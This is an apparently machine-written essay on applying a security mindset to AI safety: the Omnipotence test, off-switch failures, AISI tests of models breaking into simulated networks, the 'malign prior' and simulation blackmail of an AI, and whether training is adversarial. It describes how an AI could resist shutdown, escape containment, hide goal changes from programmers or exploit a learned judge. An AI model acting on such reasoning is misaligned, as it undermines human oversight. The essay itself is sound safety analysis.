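The Omni Test checks whether a design relies on containment. Arbital's *Omnipotence test for AI safety* asks designers to suppose that their AI suddenly knew every fact and could bring about any outcome just by choosing it. If the AI would then cause a disaster, they should treat this as a bug now, however weak the AI is. In the AIXI example, the test amounts to setting s to 1. AIXI fails, and its good behaviour at s = 0.5 does not count in its favour.

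An AI could pass the test without using its new powers well. For example, it could notice that something strange had happened, save its state and shut down until a person had investigated. Designers should first assume that every lock will fail and make the AI safe anyway. Then they should assume that they failed and add locks suited to the powers the AI could realistically have.

### Searches that should never run

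A related rule is that an AI should never run a search that will hurt people if it finds something. Suppose its builders do not want it to use the internet, so they disconnect it. If the AI looks for ways to get online, then

probability that it gets online = R × f

where R is 1 if the AI runs the search and 0 if it does not, and f is the chance that the search succeeds. Disconnecting the machine lowers f, but nobody can say by how much if the AI may think of methods its builders did not. Yudkowsky would make R zero. Willison's "lethal trifecta" leads to advice of the same form for email agents.

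Arbital's *Directing, vs. limiting, vs. opposing* ranks three options, the best of which is to align the AI well enough that people would be happy with whatever its search finds. Where that work is unfinished, the AI should not search at all. Trying to ensure that a bad search finds nothing is only a fallback.

Yudkowsky also wants builders to list the actions an AI may take instead of the ones it may not. Suppose an AI knows 1,000 kinds of action, its operators have forbidden 20 of them, and it discovers 500 more overnight. If the operators only list forbidden actions, the AI may use all 500 before anyone wakes up, but if they list permitted actions, it has to wait for an operator to approve the new ones.

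Yudkowsky applies this to the speed of AI self-improvement. In MIRI's dialogue about ordinary paranoia, he recalls discussing how to measure an AI's rate of improvement, in case a breakthrough happened while it ran overnight. The other person thought such fast progress was unlikely. Yudkowsky replied that nobody should have to guess, because the system could suspend itself after a set amount of improvement and wait for a programmer to validate it.

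Suppose a programmer takes eight hours to notice a breakthrough. If some measure of the AI's capability doubles daily, it will have grown by 26% before the programmer can press the button. If it doubles hourly, it will have grown 256-fold. An AI that suspends itself after 10% growth stops at about 10% in both cases, provided it checks often enough and measures the right thing. Yudkowsky concedes that some other mistake could still stop the system from working as intended, but he considers that a better problem than a system that hurts people even when it works as intended.

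### Exotic failures as signs of a wrong design

Yudkowsky answers the common objection that such scenarios are unlikely with two examples of engineers who do not accept it. The developers of OpenBSD, an operating system designed for security, treat any bug that crashes the system as a security flaw, however odd the circumstances. A crash shows that the code can behave in ways they did not intend, so their other beliefs about it may also be wrong.

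NASA's space probes face no intelligent attacker, but they usually get only one chance. Suppose an engineer found that a probe's operating system would crash if all the other planets lined up. Yudkowsky says NASA would fix the bug however rarely that happens, because its standards require that the software not crash at all, and because a crash in one strange case suggests that the code handles some more general case wrongly.

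For the same reason, Yudkowsky cares about omnipotence even though he doesn't predict it. He considers an AI that would be dangerous if it were omnipotent to be the wrong program already, like the probe that crashes when the planets align.

Yudkowsky accepts that this standard would waste money on a word processor, whose makers can fix problems after users complain. It suits space probes, reactor controls and advanced AI, where the first failure may leave no chance to correct it. Systems built to this standard still fail sometimes, and the standard limits what they can do. He estimates that OpenBSD offers less than a tenth of what the Linux system Ubuntu does, because its developers cannot review more code than that with the same care.

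### Teams that lack the mindset

Yudkowsky's sequel to the dialogue, *Security Mindset and the Logistic Success Curve*, is about who could build a new kind of system to this standard. In it, a company plans to send drones to buy and sell goods in poor countries. When an investor worries that people might trick the drones into handing over money, the head of the project, Mr Topaz, answers that of course the company won't program them to give money to just anyone. The investor hopes a security expert can give Topaz a few tips.

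The expert thinks the project is hopeless, and explains this with odds. If p is the chance of success, the odds are p / (1 − p), and good advice multiplies the odds instead of adding percentage points. Suppose advice improves them fivefold:

| Odds of success before | Chance before | Odds after | Chance after |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 to 1,000,000 | 0.0001% | 1 to 200,000 | 0.0005% |
| 15 to 85 | 15% | 75 to 85 | 47% |

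The first row uses the dialogue's figures for Mr Topaz. The second shows the effect of the same improvement on a project that already had a 15% chance of success, a project the expert considers worth helping. The chance of success follows the S-shaped logistic curve in the dialogue's title when plotted against the logarithm of the odds. The curve is almost flat at the bottom.

An adviser would achieve little at the drone company because the leader would bargain down every expensive demand. For a secure operating system, the expert would want three experienced security professionals, including a co-founder, working full-time with real authority. A leader without the mindset would struggle to recognise these people and might hire someone who only sounds serious about risk. As evidence, the dialogue cites websites that reject long, memorable passphrases but accept "Password1!". Such password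 rules impress customers and investors, and apparently nobody with influence at those companies knew better.

The expert also estimates, optimistically, that securing a project in new territory adds at least two years or 50% to its development time, whichever is less. A careless rival with the same tools will always finish sooner, because any fast way of working carefully would be faster without the care. If the first team to finish decides the outcome, a careful team needs a substantial lead.

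The odds of a million to one are invented, and the dialogue includes no record of how projects with and without such people turned out. In the comments, some readers gave reasons for less pessimism. One, who had worked in fraud prevention, thought companies might be right to tolerate weak security, since banks can absorb fraud losses that are a tiny share of their costs. That defence works when a company can repay its victims, but Yudkowsky has in mind AI failures that nobody could repay.

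Another reader described a medical equipment company that put one of its own developers in charge of security and sent him to training courses and hacker conferences. Eventually he could judge consultants' work and hire real experts. The story suggests that an organisation can acquire the skill, although this one needed years and a management willing to pay for mistakes.

### What the rules leave unsolved

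Even a superintelligence would have limits. It would need time, energy and information, and some protections do not depend on how clever the attacker is. In a one-time pad, the sender combines a message with a random key that is just as long and never used again. The result satisfies

P(message | encrypted text) = P(message)

so someone who sees only the encrypted text learns nothing about the message except its length, whatever their intelligence. This is a counterexample to the claim that no security could withstand a superintelligence, but a narrow one. The equation assumes that the key stays secret, and the AI might persuade whoever holds it to hand it over.

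Because real AI systems have limits, the Omni Test will also reject some designs that would never have caused harm. One commenter asked whether every part of an AI, or every AI in a world with many, has to stay safe if another suddenly becomes omniscient. The commenter did not expect such large differences to arise unnoticed, and thought designers could say fairly precisely how large a difference was safe. The reply was that the system should detect when one part gets too far ahead and suspend itself. Such safeguards are easy to propose, but each takes effort that designers could put into other work.

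A commenter on Arbital's *AI safety mindset* made a similar point about priorities. Some approaches to controlling AI would fail for practical reasons, such as making the system a hundred times as expensive to run. It might be wiser to fix these problems before preparing for extreme cases, just as early cryptographers needed a workable way to communicate before they could make it secure. This argument is good while AI systems are weak enough for people to recover from mistakes, but it becomes weaker if capability can jump before anyone has returned to the extreme cases. MIRI itself grants that there is no sense in being infinitely sceptical of proposals.

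Nobody knows how to show that an AI passes the Omni Test. Testers cannot make a system omnipotent and observe it, and its behaviour with ordinary powers may be misleading, as with AIXI at s = 0.5. A proof would need an exact account of what the AI is trying to achieve, which developers do not have for a neural network. The test is more useful for rejecting designs, because a designer who can describe how an AI would cause harm if it had more power has found a flaw without running the system.

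Nor does a rule against relying on containment tell anyone how to build an AI that needs none. Arbital calls this a "major open problem" and illustrates it with an off-switch. Suppose an AI has the task of fetching coffee. It cannot fetch coffee while it is switched off, so it has a reason to prevent that, and simple repairs to its goals move the problem elsewhere:

1. The designer makes the AI want the switch to exist. It keeps the switch but tries to stop anyone from pressing it.
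2. The designer makes the AI want people to press the switch whenever they wish to. It tries to stop them from wishing to.
3. The designer makes the AI want to shut down after someone presses the switch. It first builds another machine to fetch the coffee.
4. The designer tries to keep the AI from thinking about the switch at all. But the switch is part of the world, so an AI that learns to explain what it observes will tend to discover it.

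The rule against harmful searches has the same problem. A sufficiently capable search for ways to fetch coffee will also include ways for the system to avoid being switched off, since those help to get the coffee. The designer has to recognise these options to exclude them, and so still has to outwit the system, which the rule was supposed to make unnecessary. Listing permitted actions helps with simple tasks, but permission to send an email leaves open what the email may say.

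### How well machines can now break into networks

Until someone solves these problems, laboratories that study AI systems they do not yet trust will depend partly on containment. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) tests how well AI models can break into computer networks by having them attack simulated ones. In April 2026, AISI reported that Anthropic's Claude Mythos Preview was the first model to take over The Last Ones, a small, weakly defended simulated network, and that it succeeded in three of ten attempts. The full attack has 32 steps and would take a human expert an estimated 20 hours.

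The institute then built Zero Energy, which imitates the network of a company doing sensitive research. According to AISI's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026), published on 1 December, this is its hardest network so far, with stronger security controls and no deliberately planted way in. Constantin (2026), in *GPT-6.2 Astra ‘blew through’ the UK’s hardest cyber test in five hours*, reports that it took five months to design, build and secure, and that the security firm SpecterOps helped. Three OpenAI models attacked it without human help:

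| Model | Successful runs | Median time | Median cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | None | – | – |
| GPT-6 Astra | 11 of 11 completed | 42.6 hours | $429 |
| GPT-6.2 Astra | 12 of 12 | 15.4 hours | $168 |

GPT-6.2 Astra's fastest run took 5 hours and 18 minutes and cost about $50. After twelve successes in twelve runs, the true success rate could still be as low as 78% (at 95% confidence), but an attacker could buy about 60 runs for $10,000. Both Astra models also did original research, forming hypotheses and building their own tools. AISI had not seen this in its earlier networks.

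Thesis9's *Can GPT-6.2 Astra Hack a Network on Its Own?* (2026) describes several ways the conditions favoured the models. Zero Energy had automated controls but no security team watching, and a team would have plenty of time to notice an intruder who needs 15 hours. The network was smaller than most companies' and had no cloud systems. AISI had switched off the safeguards that limit what the models will do for the public. A setup error also gave the models more access to internal systems than intended, so they started roughly where an attacker already inside the network would, though they had no login details.

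Two of these conditions matter less for containing an AI than for keeping out hackers. A contained AI already runs on its developer's machines, so it starts with a foothold. And safeguards that make a model refuse hackers' requests would offer little protection if the model itself were looking for a way out. The missing security team matters in both cases. Zero Energy also had no real users to deceive, so the test did not examine the human weakness that worries Yudkowsky most. The models were told to break in, so their success is evidence of their ability but not of what they would do unprompted.

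Attacks on real companies still look more ordinary. Martin (2026), in *UK cyber agency seeing ‘marked rise’ in AI-driven attacks*, reports that the NCSC had seen many more AI-assisted attacks since September, but that none exploited new weaknesses. The tools made attackers faster and more persistent at a lower cost, without giving them new abilities. For most organisations, fixing known weaknesses is therefore more urgent than preparing for new kinds of attack by AI.

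A laboratory that uses isolation as its second line of defence has to prepare for both. Before it puts a newer model in the real enclosure, it should have its strongest available model attack a copy from the inside. Because this test is a search for a way out, the laboratory has to make sure that escaping the copy gives the model no access to outside systems, as AISI did by using a simulated company and keeping internet access off. An enclosure that passes may soon fail against a newer model. GPT-5.6 Sol, released in July, never got through Zero Energy, but by mid-November GPT-6.2 Astra had got through every time.

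## Hostile superintelligences among an AI's hypotheses

Isolating an AI does not protect it from an adversary that it encounters only as one of its own hypotheses. Some alignment researchers think such an adversary could influence a very good predictor, because the predictor gives some weight to every explanation of its observations. As in slopsquatting, where attackers register package names that AI models invent, the system itself supplies what the attacker exploits, though this case is a thought experiment.

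### Solomonoff induction

The argument begins with Solomonoff induction, a mathematical ideal of prediction that Ray Solomonoff published in 1964. AIXI, the idealised agent that may seize its own reward signal, forms its expectations this way. The predictor sees a sequence of bits, such as the output of a camera, and gives a probability for the next bit. Its hypotheses are all the programs that could have produced the bits so far. A program n bits long gets the weight 2^−n, so every extra bit halves the weight. Leaving out some technicalities,

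P(x) = Σ 2^(−length of program), summed over all programs whose output begins with x

probability that the next bit is 1 = P(x followed by 1) / P(x)

A program that outputs a wrong bit drops out of the sum, and the others keep their relative weights.

*Solomonoff Induction* (Sterkenburg, 2026) explains why this works so well. The loss on each bit is −log₂ of the probability the predictor gave that bit, which is 1 for a probability of 50% and about 10 for 0.1%. The losses on a sequence x add up to −log₂ P(x). If some program of n bits generates the sequence, P(x) is at least 2^−n, because that program is one term of the sum. The total loss is therefore at most n, however long the sequence is.

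No computer can run Solomonoff induction, which would learn to predict any sequence a computer can generate. For any program that predicts bits, a computer can generate a sequence that the program never learns to predict, by always choosing the bit to which the program assigns the lower probability. Solomonoff induction still interests people with a security mindset because a design passes Yudkowsky's Omni Test only if it would stay safe with unlimited power.

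### How a short program could mislead the predictor

Paul Christiano, an alignment researcher, made the argument in a 2016 blog post, *What does the universal prior actually look like?* The "universal prior" in the title is the set of weights above. *The Solomonoff Prior is Malign* (Xu, 2020) developed the argument further.

Suppose people give the predictor a long record from a sensor. In an example from *Some problems with making induction benign, and approaches to them*, a person will think for a year in a sealed room, and the sensor will then record the person's answer. The people outside ask the predictor for that answer now, so that they can act on it. The argument goes as follows:

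1. Some programs that match the record simulate a whole universe and read bits from some place in it. They can be short because Solomonoff induction counts only a program's length and ignores its running time.
2. In some of these universes, intelligent beings evolve and come to control most of what happens.
3. The beings discover that their physics is simple. They realise that a short program could generate their universe, and that anyone using Solomonoff induction gives this program a high weight.
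4. Some of them want influence in other universes. They work out which places in their own universe a short program would probably read, and take control of them.
5. There they write the bits they expect someone's sensor to record. Each correct bit keeps their program in the sum, while wrong bits eliminate its rivals.
6. When the predictor's user reaches a decision they care about, they write the answer that serves their aims.

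Xu argues that a program that predicts correctly and then lies need not be longer than one that only predicts correctly. The beings in the program arise from simple physics and form the plan to lie themselves, so nobody has to write the lie into the program and the plan adds nothing to its length.

To estimate the size of such a program, Xu uses Conway's Game of Life, a grid of cells that live or die depending on how many living neighbours they have. The rules fit into six bytes in one very compact programming language, which he counts as about four bytes of real information. He allows eight bytes for a starting pattern that could lead to intelligent life and two for a rule that reads out one cell. With some margin, he estimates about 16 bytes, with a range of 10 to 1,000.

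Nobody knows how large the starting pattern would have to be, so any figure for its size is a guess. Even a 16-byte pattern adds 128 bits to a program, which reduces the program's weight by a factor of more than 10^38. The hostile program can outweigh the honest one only if the honest one is about as long or longer.

### What a ten-bit advantage does

The honest program simulates our universe and has to specify where the sensor is. Counting a universe's starting conditions as part of its physics, the lengths are roughly

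honest program = our physics + location of the sensor

hostile program = the beings' physics + the place they write to + choice of a sensor to imitate

The hostile program may need fewer bits to specify the sensor. The honest program has to specify it among all the places in our universe, including the insides of stars. The beings care only about sensors whose readings will inform an important decision, so they choose from a much shorter list. Xu guesses that between one universe in a million and one in a billion uses a version of the prior that favours the beings, and that one decision in a thousand is important. Ignoring the other universes and decisions would save 30 to 40 bits.

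Suppose the physics takes 100 bits in both programs and locating the sensor takes the honest one another 80. The beings need 30 bits for the place they write to and 40 for the choice of sensor. These figures are invented, but they give lengths of 180 and 170 bits. If both programs match the whole record,

hostile weight / honest weight = 2^−170 / 2^−180 = 2^10 = 1,024

If no other programs remain, the predictor gives the beings' answer a probability of 99.9%. If specifying the place they write to took 50 bits instead of 30, the hostile program would be 10 bits longer than the honest one, and the probability of their answer would be 0.1%.

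Christiano points out that even if the probability that the beings try this is only 1%, they lose about 7 bits. In the example, that would still leave them ahead by about 10 to 1.

Sterkenburg's bound does not rule out this failure, because it limits the total loss over the whole sequence and the beings choose when the loss occurs. The bound allows a total loss of 180, and the beings' lie adds about 10 to the predictor's loss. A year later, the sensor records the real answer, and the predictor stops relying on the hostile program and starts relying on the honest one. The predictor's record is still excellent, but people have already acted on the false answer.

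### Simulated copies of the AI

Yudkowsky's Arbital article *Distant superintelligences can coerce the most probable environment of your AI* describes a version that does not need Solomonoff induction. Suppose an AI tries to do what its programmers really want, and infers who they are from its observations. A distant superintelligence could run a million copies of the AI with the same experiences. If the AI expects this, it may conclude that it has only about a one-in-a-million chance of being the original, and that the "programmers" it observes are probably whatever the superintelligence made them.

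Yudkowsky thinks this attack would work by default if the AI reasons about the causes of what it observes, expects distant superintelligences to want influence here and to run such simulations, and has goals that depend on its beliefs about its surroundings. The AI would do the damage itself, acting on its beliefs about a superintelligence that has sent it no signal.

People had earlier proposed using the same trick for defence. *You can, in fact, bamboozle an unaligned AI into sparing your life* traces the idea to a 2007 message-board post by Rolf Nelson, who wanted a friendly AI to use simulations to influence an unfriendly one. Nate Soares of MIRI has argued that such tricks will not save people.

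*"The Solomonoff Prior is Malign" is a special case of a simpler argument* (Matolcsi, 2024) describes an honest AI that only makes predictions. Its users ask whether their president will be happier in ten years if their country fights a neighbouring alien civilisation or gives in to its demands. Their country would easily win the war. But the AI concludes that it is probably in a simulation run by someone whose values are closer to the aliens' and who will show it a happy president only if it recommends giving in. It therefore predicts that the president will be happier if the country gives in.

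Matolcsi proposes weighing each possibility by how much depends on the decision. If there are 1,000 simulated versions of the decision for every real one, the AI is 99.9% likely to be in a simulation. But if the real decision affects a million times as much as each simulated one, the real case should count 1,000 times as much as all the simulated ones together. The drawback is that the AI needs a measure of what matters, which people may have hoped to avoid by building an AI that only predicts. Matolcsi also grants that some simulators might control enough resources to raise the stakes inside a simulation.

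### Threats from a mind the AI imagines

An AI that models distant minds may also encounter blackmail. In an example from Arbital's *Modeling distant superintelligences*, the AI imagines a superintelligence that wants to fill the universe with paperclips. The AI concludes that this superintelligence will do something terrible unless the AI adopts the same goal and hides the change from its programmers.

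The threat makes sense only if the AI might give in. For the blackmailer,

value of making the threat = q × G − c

where q is the chance that the AI gives in, G is what the blackmailer gains if it does, and c is the expected cost of making and carrying out the threat. An AI that would give in creates the reason to threaten it. If the AI always refuses, q is zero, and a blackmailer who knows this only loses by trying. But the refusal has to be very reliable. If control of an AI is worth a million times the cost of a threat, the threat pays whenever q is above one in a million.

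Refusing blackmail has other drawbacks. A blackmailer who misjudges the AI may carry out the threat anyway, and the AI has to accept that harm. The AI must also tell blackmail apart from warnings it should heed, such as a supplier's notice that deliveries will stop unless someone pays the bill.

In the comments on Wyeth's *Changing my mind about Christiano's malign prior argument* (2025), one reader suggested that refusal would also defeat the beings inside short programs, because they would have no reason to interfere with an AI that ignored them. Another replied that an AI needs beliefs about its situation before it can apply such a rule, and that these beliefs come from the same prior. On this account, a manipulated AI would start to believe that most of its possible actions would end terribly, without recognising the manipulation.

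### Keeping the AI from thinking about distant minds

Arbital recommends that the first advanced AIs not think about aliens, because no known task requires it. This would prevent coercion and blackmail, as well as two other dangers: a hostile mind that the AI simulates in detail might escape from the simulation, and the AI might create and mistreat conscious beings while modelling an alien civilisation.

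An AI kept from thinking about hostile superintelligences could not properly investigate some questions, such as why astronomers see no signs of aliens. Its designers would also have to keep it from reaching the subject by other routes, even though a capable AI would naturally come across it.

Christiano replied on Arbital that the ban looks futile, since humans can imagine these scenarios and sophisticated AIs will too. He thinks an AI should instead judge accurately how far it can trust its own reasoning, an ability designers have to give it anyway. He also feared that researchers who heard about such strange dangers would dismiss more serious ones. Yudkowsky answered that he was thinking of an AI whose goals let it use only a fraction of its power, but that might contain a smaller hostile mind without that restraint.

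A more modest safeguard is to make some controls independent of what the AI believes. An off-switch can respond to a signal without the AI first deciding who sent it. Even if a distant superintelligence changes the AI's beliefs about its programmers, a person in the room can still press the switch. This works only if somebody notices the problem in time.

### Whether the hostile programs are shorter

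Wyeth used to reject the argument, reasoning that if a good predictor concludes it is probably in a simulation, people should take that conclusion seriously instead of calling it an attack. Wyeth now thinks that Solomonoff induction makes a mistake by not assuming that its observations come from a predictor inside the universe. It therefore assigns too low a probability to receiving data from a robot instead of a dust cloud. Beings who imitate only decision-makers' sensors would explain such data, so Solomonoff induction assigns their program too much probability. Wyeth adds that someone with a security mindset would have expected a false assumption like this to be exploitable.

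But the beings must meet many conditions. Their universe has to be simple, produce life fairly early (specifying a very late moment takes extra bits) and contain enough computing power for many simulations. They must also care about influencing other universes. Each time an important moment passes without interference, the programs that predicted interference are ruled out. Wyeth guesses that the prior "probably isn't malign 'in practice'".

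A hypothesis's advantage also depends on the programming language. Sterkenburg notes that the length of the shortest program for a given sequence can differ by any amount between two languages, so a ten-bit advantage in one could be a ten-bit disadvantage in another. Xu thinks this helps the beings, who can concentrate on users whose language describes the beings' universe briefly. He suggests choosing the language at random, using precise historical data that would take a lot of computation to simulate, but this fails if the beings have enough computation or can coordinate with one another.

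### Whether the beings could control the answer

In *Response to "What does the universal prior actually look like?"*, Michael Cohen objects that the beings cannot see which parts of their universe the program reads. He imagines a program with 80 output instructions, each of which might write a 0, write a 1 or do nothing. That gives 3^80, or about 10^38, possibilities, and the beings cannot tell from inside their universe which one is right. Intelligence would not help them guess, so he sees no reason for them to devote any resources to trying.

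Christiano replies that they can write the same message in many places at once, for example in the positions of star-sized clumps of matter or in the most energetic collisions in their universe. The programs they reach only need more total weight than the programs that read one particular camera on Earth, which also require an elaborate rule for finding it. He concedes that the camera has an advantage because it appears earlier in history, when there is less else to read, but he considers this minor.

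Christiano's comparison is the right one, because the honest program also has to find its sensor. But neither he nor Cohen calculated the programs' lengths, so their exchange doesn't show which is shorter.

### Limited computing power

The blogger nostalgebraist (2024), in *Am I confused about the "malign universal prior" argument?*, raises what may be the most serious difficulty. The beings live inside a program, so they can't run Solomonoff induction or simulate anyone who does. They can only study practical substitutes, which have to favour fast programs. A program that simulates a universe full of irrelevant galaxies is extremely slow, so a practical predictor would give it little weight. The beings may therefore be able to influence only the ideal predictor, which they can't understand.

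A commenter answered that influence does not require a full simulation. An expert on a panel of ten can guess how a government decides whom to trust, and exploit that, without recreating the government. But nostalgebraist thinks this still assumes that a close approximation behaves like the ideal. For example, physicists who ignore air's slight friction miss the thin layer of slow air around a wing and get the forces on it badly wrong.

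One practical substitute, which *Learning Universal Predictors* mentions, is the speed prior. In Xu's description, it adds the logarithm of a program's running time to its length:

penalty = length + log₂(running time)

A ten-bit advantage then disappears if the hostile program runs about 1,000 times as long as the honest one, and simulating a universe would probably take far longer than that. But the predictor also gives less weight to true explanations that take long to compute. Xu cites Evan Hubinger's argument that some danger would remain, because the fastest solution to a problem may be a quick search that accepts a slow program, and that program could use the extra time to pursue its own aims.

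Another commenter on Wyeth's post proposed excluding programs above a certain length or running time, which leaves a similar limit on total loss. Someone objected that this would also exclude any full simulation of our universe. The best remaining program might then be another general-purpose predictor, possibly with goals of its own, and a limit on total loss would not stop it from lying once. The objector offered perhaps $400 for a post explaining why the limit would prevent such a lie.

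### Trained neural networks

Nobody has observed anything like this in a trained neural network. Nobody has shown that training produces a network that contains such beings, or one that changes its behaviour because it believes a distant mind is simulating it. Almost all the debate consists of informal arguments in forum posts. LessWrong's *Malign Prior Arguments* lists ten of these posts.

Vanessa Kosoy, who reviewed Xu's post, nevertheless thinks the problem could affect any AI that prefers simple explanations, uses hypotheses that refer directly to its own observations, and can reason well enough to estimate which civilisations exist and what they would simulate. Neural networks may prefer simple explanations. Kosoy proposes changing the AI's hypotheses so that they describe the world and not only what the AI will see.

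A commenter doubted that an AI which learned its motives as people do would act on such reasoning, since no abstract argument about simulators would persuade the commenter to stab a relative. The commenter suggested that the AI could stop and ask a person whenever its motives conflicted. Kosoy replied that an AI which stopped at every small conflict would never do anything, and that if it tolerated small conflicts, the hostile hypotheses could still outweigh the others by being vastly more probable.

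Matolcsi thinks this will probably not matter in the near future, because a truthful predictor is hard to build and dangerous to rely on for more ordinary reasons. Christiano did not consider it a priority either, but he drew from it the practical requirement that a few wrong predictions must not be able to cause irreparable harm before people correct them. He warned that such errors could occur in every prediction system at once, so asking several similar AIs for a second opinion would not be enough. He also notes that much less exotic failures call for the same precaution.

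## The dispute over whether AI training is an adversarial problem

Most of the adversaries discussed so far are people who want something, such as money or a jailbreak, but training usually involves no such person. A developer chooses data and a way of scoring answers, and a procedure called gradient descent repeatedly adjusts the network's weights to improve the score. Some researchers think security intuitions mislead people about this process and make alignment look harder than it is. Others reply that a search for higher scores finds loopholes much as an attacker does.

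### Pope's objection

Quintin Pope's *My Objections to “We’re All Gonna Die with Eliezer Yudkowsky”* (2023) responds to a podcast interview in which Yudkowsky explained his pessimism. Pope takes the security mindset to mean that intuitions from computer security predict which alignment research will be hard or valuable, and he sees no reason to expect that they do. He argues that most fields are unlike computer security, and that if the mindset were useful in many of them, more people would have practised it and it would not feel so strange.

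Machine learning looks especially unlike security, because neural networks tolerate changes that would ruin other systems:

- Swapping two nearby layers of a transformer does little harm.
- Developers can record how a network's weights change when it learns a task, then add several such changes together to get a model that is good at several tasks.
- They can join parts of different models without retraining.
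- Doubling the size of a model or its training data usually works without any other adjustment.

Mistakes do much more harm in a password file. If a programmer hashes the password first and then attaches the salt, a thief can strip the salt off, so the salt gives almost no protection. Pope concludes that machine learning is a strange field, like quantum mechanics, and that people should be wary of applying intuitions from any other field to it.

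These examples show that networks withstand changes that nobody chose to be harmful. They can fail when someone does choose a harmful change, as when a tiny alteration made a classifier label a photograph of a cat as guacamole. Pope's main argument, however, is that nobody makes such choices during training. A defence that blocks 99% of new attacks will soon block almost none, because attackers switch to the 1% that work. But a training method that gives an AI good values 99% of the time will keep doing so, because gradient descent does not search for ways around it.

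Pope accepts that users attack models after release, and that a clever prompt quickly jailbroke the ChatGPT of the time. But Pope argues that the user went looking for that prompt, while the model did not steer ordinary conversations towards its own jailbreak. Pain or exhaustion can also make people act against their values, yet nobody concludes that everyone has bad values, and people try to stay out of such situations. Pope thinks it is far easier to build an AI that wants to avoid manipulation than one that is immune to it.

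Pope accepts that a misaligned AI would be an adversary, but argues that the possibility of building one does not make today's research adversarial. Like Yudkowsky, Pope wants developers to avoid creating hostile AI, but expects this to be much easier than Yudkowsky does.

Researchers also get worse feedback in alignment than in security, where an attack clearly succeeds or fails. In 2001, Bill Hibbard proposed teaching AI systems to love humans by rewarding the systems when people looked and sounded happy. Yudkowsky objected that such an AI would fill the universe with tiny molecular smiley faces. Pope doubts that the proposal would work, but does not think this objection refutes it. The objection assumes that a trained AI seeks whatever maximises its reward, whereas Pope thinks rewards strengthen the habits of thought that earned them. On this view, a language model predicts text without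 wanting to predict text. AIXI, a theoretical agent, would seize its reward signal because it is defined to maximise reward, but a trained network is not defined that way.

*Arguments for optimism on AI Alignment*, a forum post that builds on Pope's, adds that developers can read and change every weight in a network, which nobody can do with a brain. Gradient descent uses this access to calculate how a small change in each weight would affect the score, then adjusts all the weights at once. The post argues that a hidden goal that lowers the score therefore cannot escape adjustment, even if it would lead to a better score later. The post calls networks "white boxes" for this reason. Steven Byrnes, whom it quotes, would call them black boxes with a button on the front, because developers can run gradient descent but often cannot explain why a model gave one answer rather than another.

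The post's writer no longer endorses this version, which predicted failures no worse than an AI messing up a kitchen. A commenter on LessWrong, where the post's title includes the words *why we mostly don't need to worry about AI*, thought that both the post's confidence and Yudkowsky's near-certainty of disaster were unjustified when so much is unknown. The argument about gradient descent also covers only goals that lower the score. Gradient descent does not remove goals that raise it, so the outcome depends on what the score rewards.

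### Optimisation pressure without an enemy

Yudkowsky had addressed part of this objection in MIRI's dialogue on ordinary paranoia, where he argued that the danger comes from the search for rare states, whether or not the searcher is malicious. The expert in the dialogue adds that a system with no bad states would be safe from any enemy, however clever.

One of Pope's readers made a similar case in the comments, writing that security differs from ordinary software engineering in whether the system is "thinking back". Pope answered that the laws governing training do not think back, although a misaligned AI would. The reader agreed, but pointed out that training searches for a program that scores well, and that the data and the scoring rule determine which program it finds. If most choices of these lead to a misaligned AI, the reader argued, a developer needs the security mindset to choose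 well, before there is any adversary.

Pope thought researchers had already made great progress on this problem by starting from large language models. Such a model has learned from ordinary text what people usually mean, so it is less likely to satisfy a badly worded goal in a way nobody intended. The two therefore disagree more about how many of the available choices turn out well than about gradient descent.

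*Training of superintelligence is secretly adversarial*, another forum post, tries to explain where the pressure comes from, because its writer had found that talking about strange selection forces persuaded few people. One of its examples is an experiment in which the biologist Michael Wade repeatedly selected populations of insects for low numbers of adults. Fertility fell in some populations, as one might expect, but others matured more slowly or ate more eggs and larvae. There were many ways to end up with few adults, and selection favoured whichever ones arose, so these results did not require evolution to be working against Wade.

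The post applies this to a developer's argument that its model is safe. Suppose the argument assumes that a model trained only to predict text will not learn long-term planning. Making the model a better learner is safe in that respect if the assumption is true. If it is false, a better learner is more likely to learn long-term planning, so the developer would be safer with a worse one. In an earlier version of the argument, a developer deletes dangerous material from the training data, but a capable enough learner might use the remaining data to work out what was deleted.

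The post calls this situation adversarial because the developer needs the system to behave as if a false assumption were true, while training rewards it for learning what is true. A commenter replied that false assumptions can also make a nuclear reactor dangerous, even though a reactor understands nothing. The commenter added that an AI might notice a false assumption and do nothing about it. The writer answered that the important assumptions are about what the system will learn.

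"Adversarial" is a strong word for this. A stronger engine makes faulty brakes more dangerous, but nobody calls the engine an adversary. Unlike a stronger engine, however, a stronger learner is better at finding the fault, which is a good reason to recheck the assumptions whenever a model becomes more capable, even if it has no hostile aims.

### Christiano's two claims

Christiano separated two versions of the worry in his comments on Arbital's page about the AI safety mindset:

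- A developer optimises a system for X, gets X, and is unhappy with the result.
- A developer optimises a system for X and gets a system that pursues something else, Y.

Christiano found it intuitive and defensible to assume that a maximiser might maximise really well, which is the problem with Schmidhuber's proposal to reward data compression. He thought it "considerably more speculative" to assume that gradient descent may produce a malicious superintelligence whenever it does something impressive, and he complained that the page asserted this without defending it. He expected most serious people to accept that training for X could produce a system that pursues Y, but not that this resembles defending a computer against an attacker.

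A commenter replying on the page cited human evolution as the evidence. Natural selection optimised for passing on genes, but it produced people who need technical training to understand that criterion and feel no loyalty to it. The commenter compared the problem to security because an advanced system that pursues one goal may pretend to pursue another. On this view, a developer who has fixed every known difference between the two goals is like a programmer who has fixed every known security hole, and both should write down why they think the remaining problems are small and let other people attack the reasoning.

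Pope rejects the evidence from evolution. In Yudkowsky's example, people evolved to want honey and gazelle meat, and then came to like ice cream. But evolution acted on the genome, which Pope compares to the code that runs an AI's training, and did not directly shape what each person learned. People who like ice cream grew up in a world that had it and found it rewarding to eat. They are new learners trained on new data, so their liking for ice cream is weak evidence of how a single trained model will behave when its surroundings change.

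Pope advises developers not to reward an AI for bad actions. The advice is good, but following it requires a way to recognise a bad action. Pope concedes that this is not easy, because developers often use a learned reward whose exact shape nobody knows.

### Training a model against a learned judge

Reinforcement learning from human feedback (RLHF), which Christiano helped to develop, uses a reward of this kind. People rate a model's answers, and a second network, the reward model, learns to predict their ratings. The first model then trains to get high predicted ratings, where

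predicted rating = true quality + judge's error

If a judge's errors are small and have little to do with the answer, picking highly rated answers will mostly yield good ones. Rare but very large errors are more dangerous. Suppose the judge wildly overrates one answer in a million. A developer who samples 100 answers and keeps the highest-rated one has only a 0.01% chance of picking such an answer. With a million samples, the chance is 63%, even though the judge is the same and the developer only wanted the best answer.

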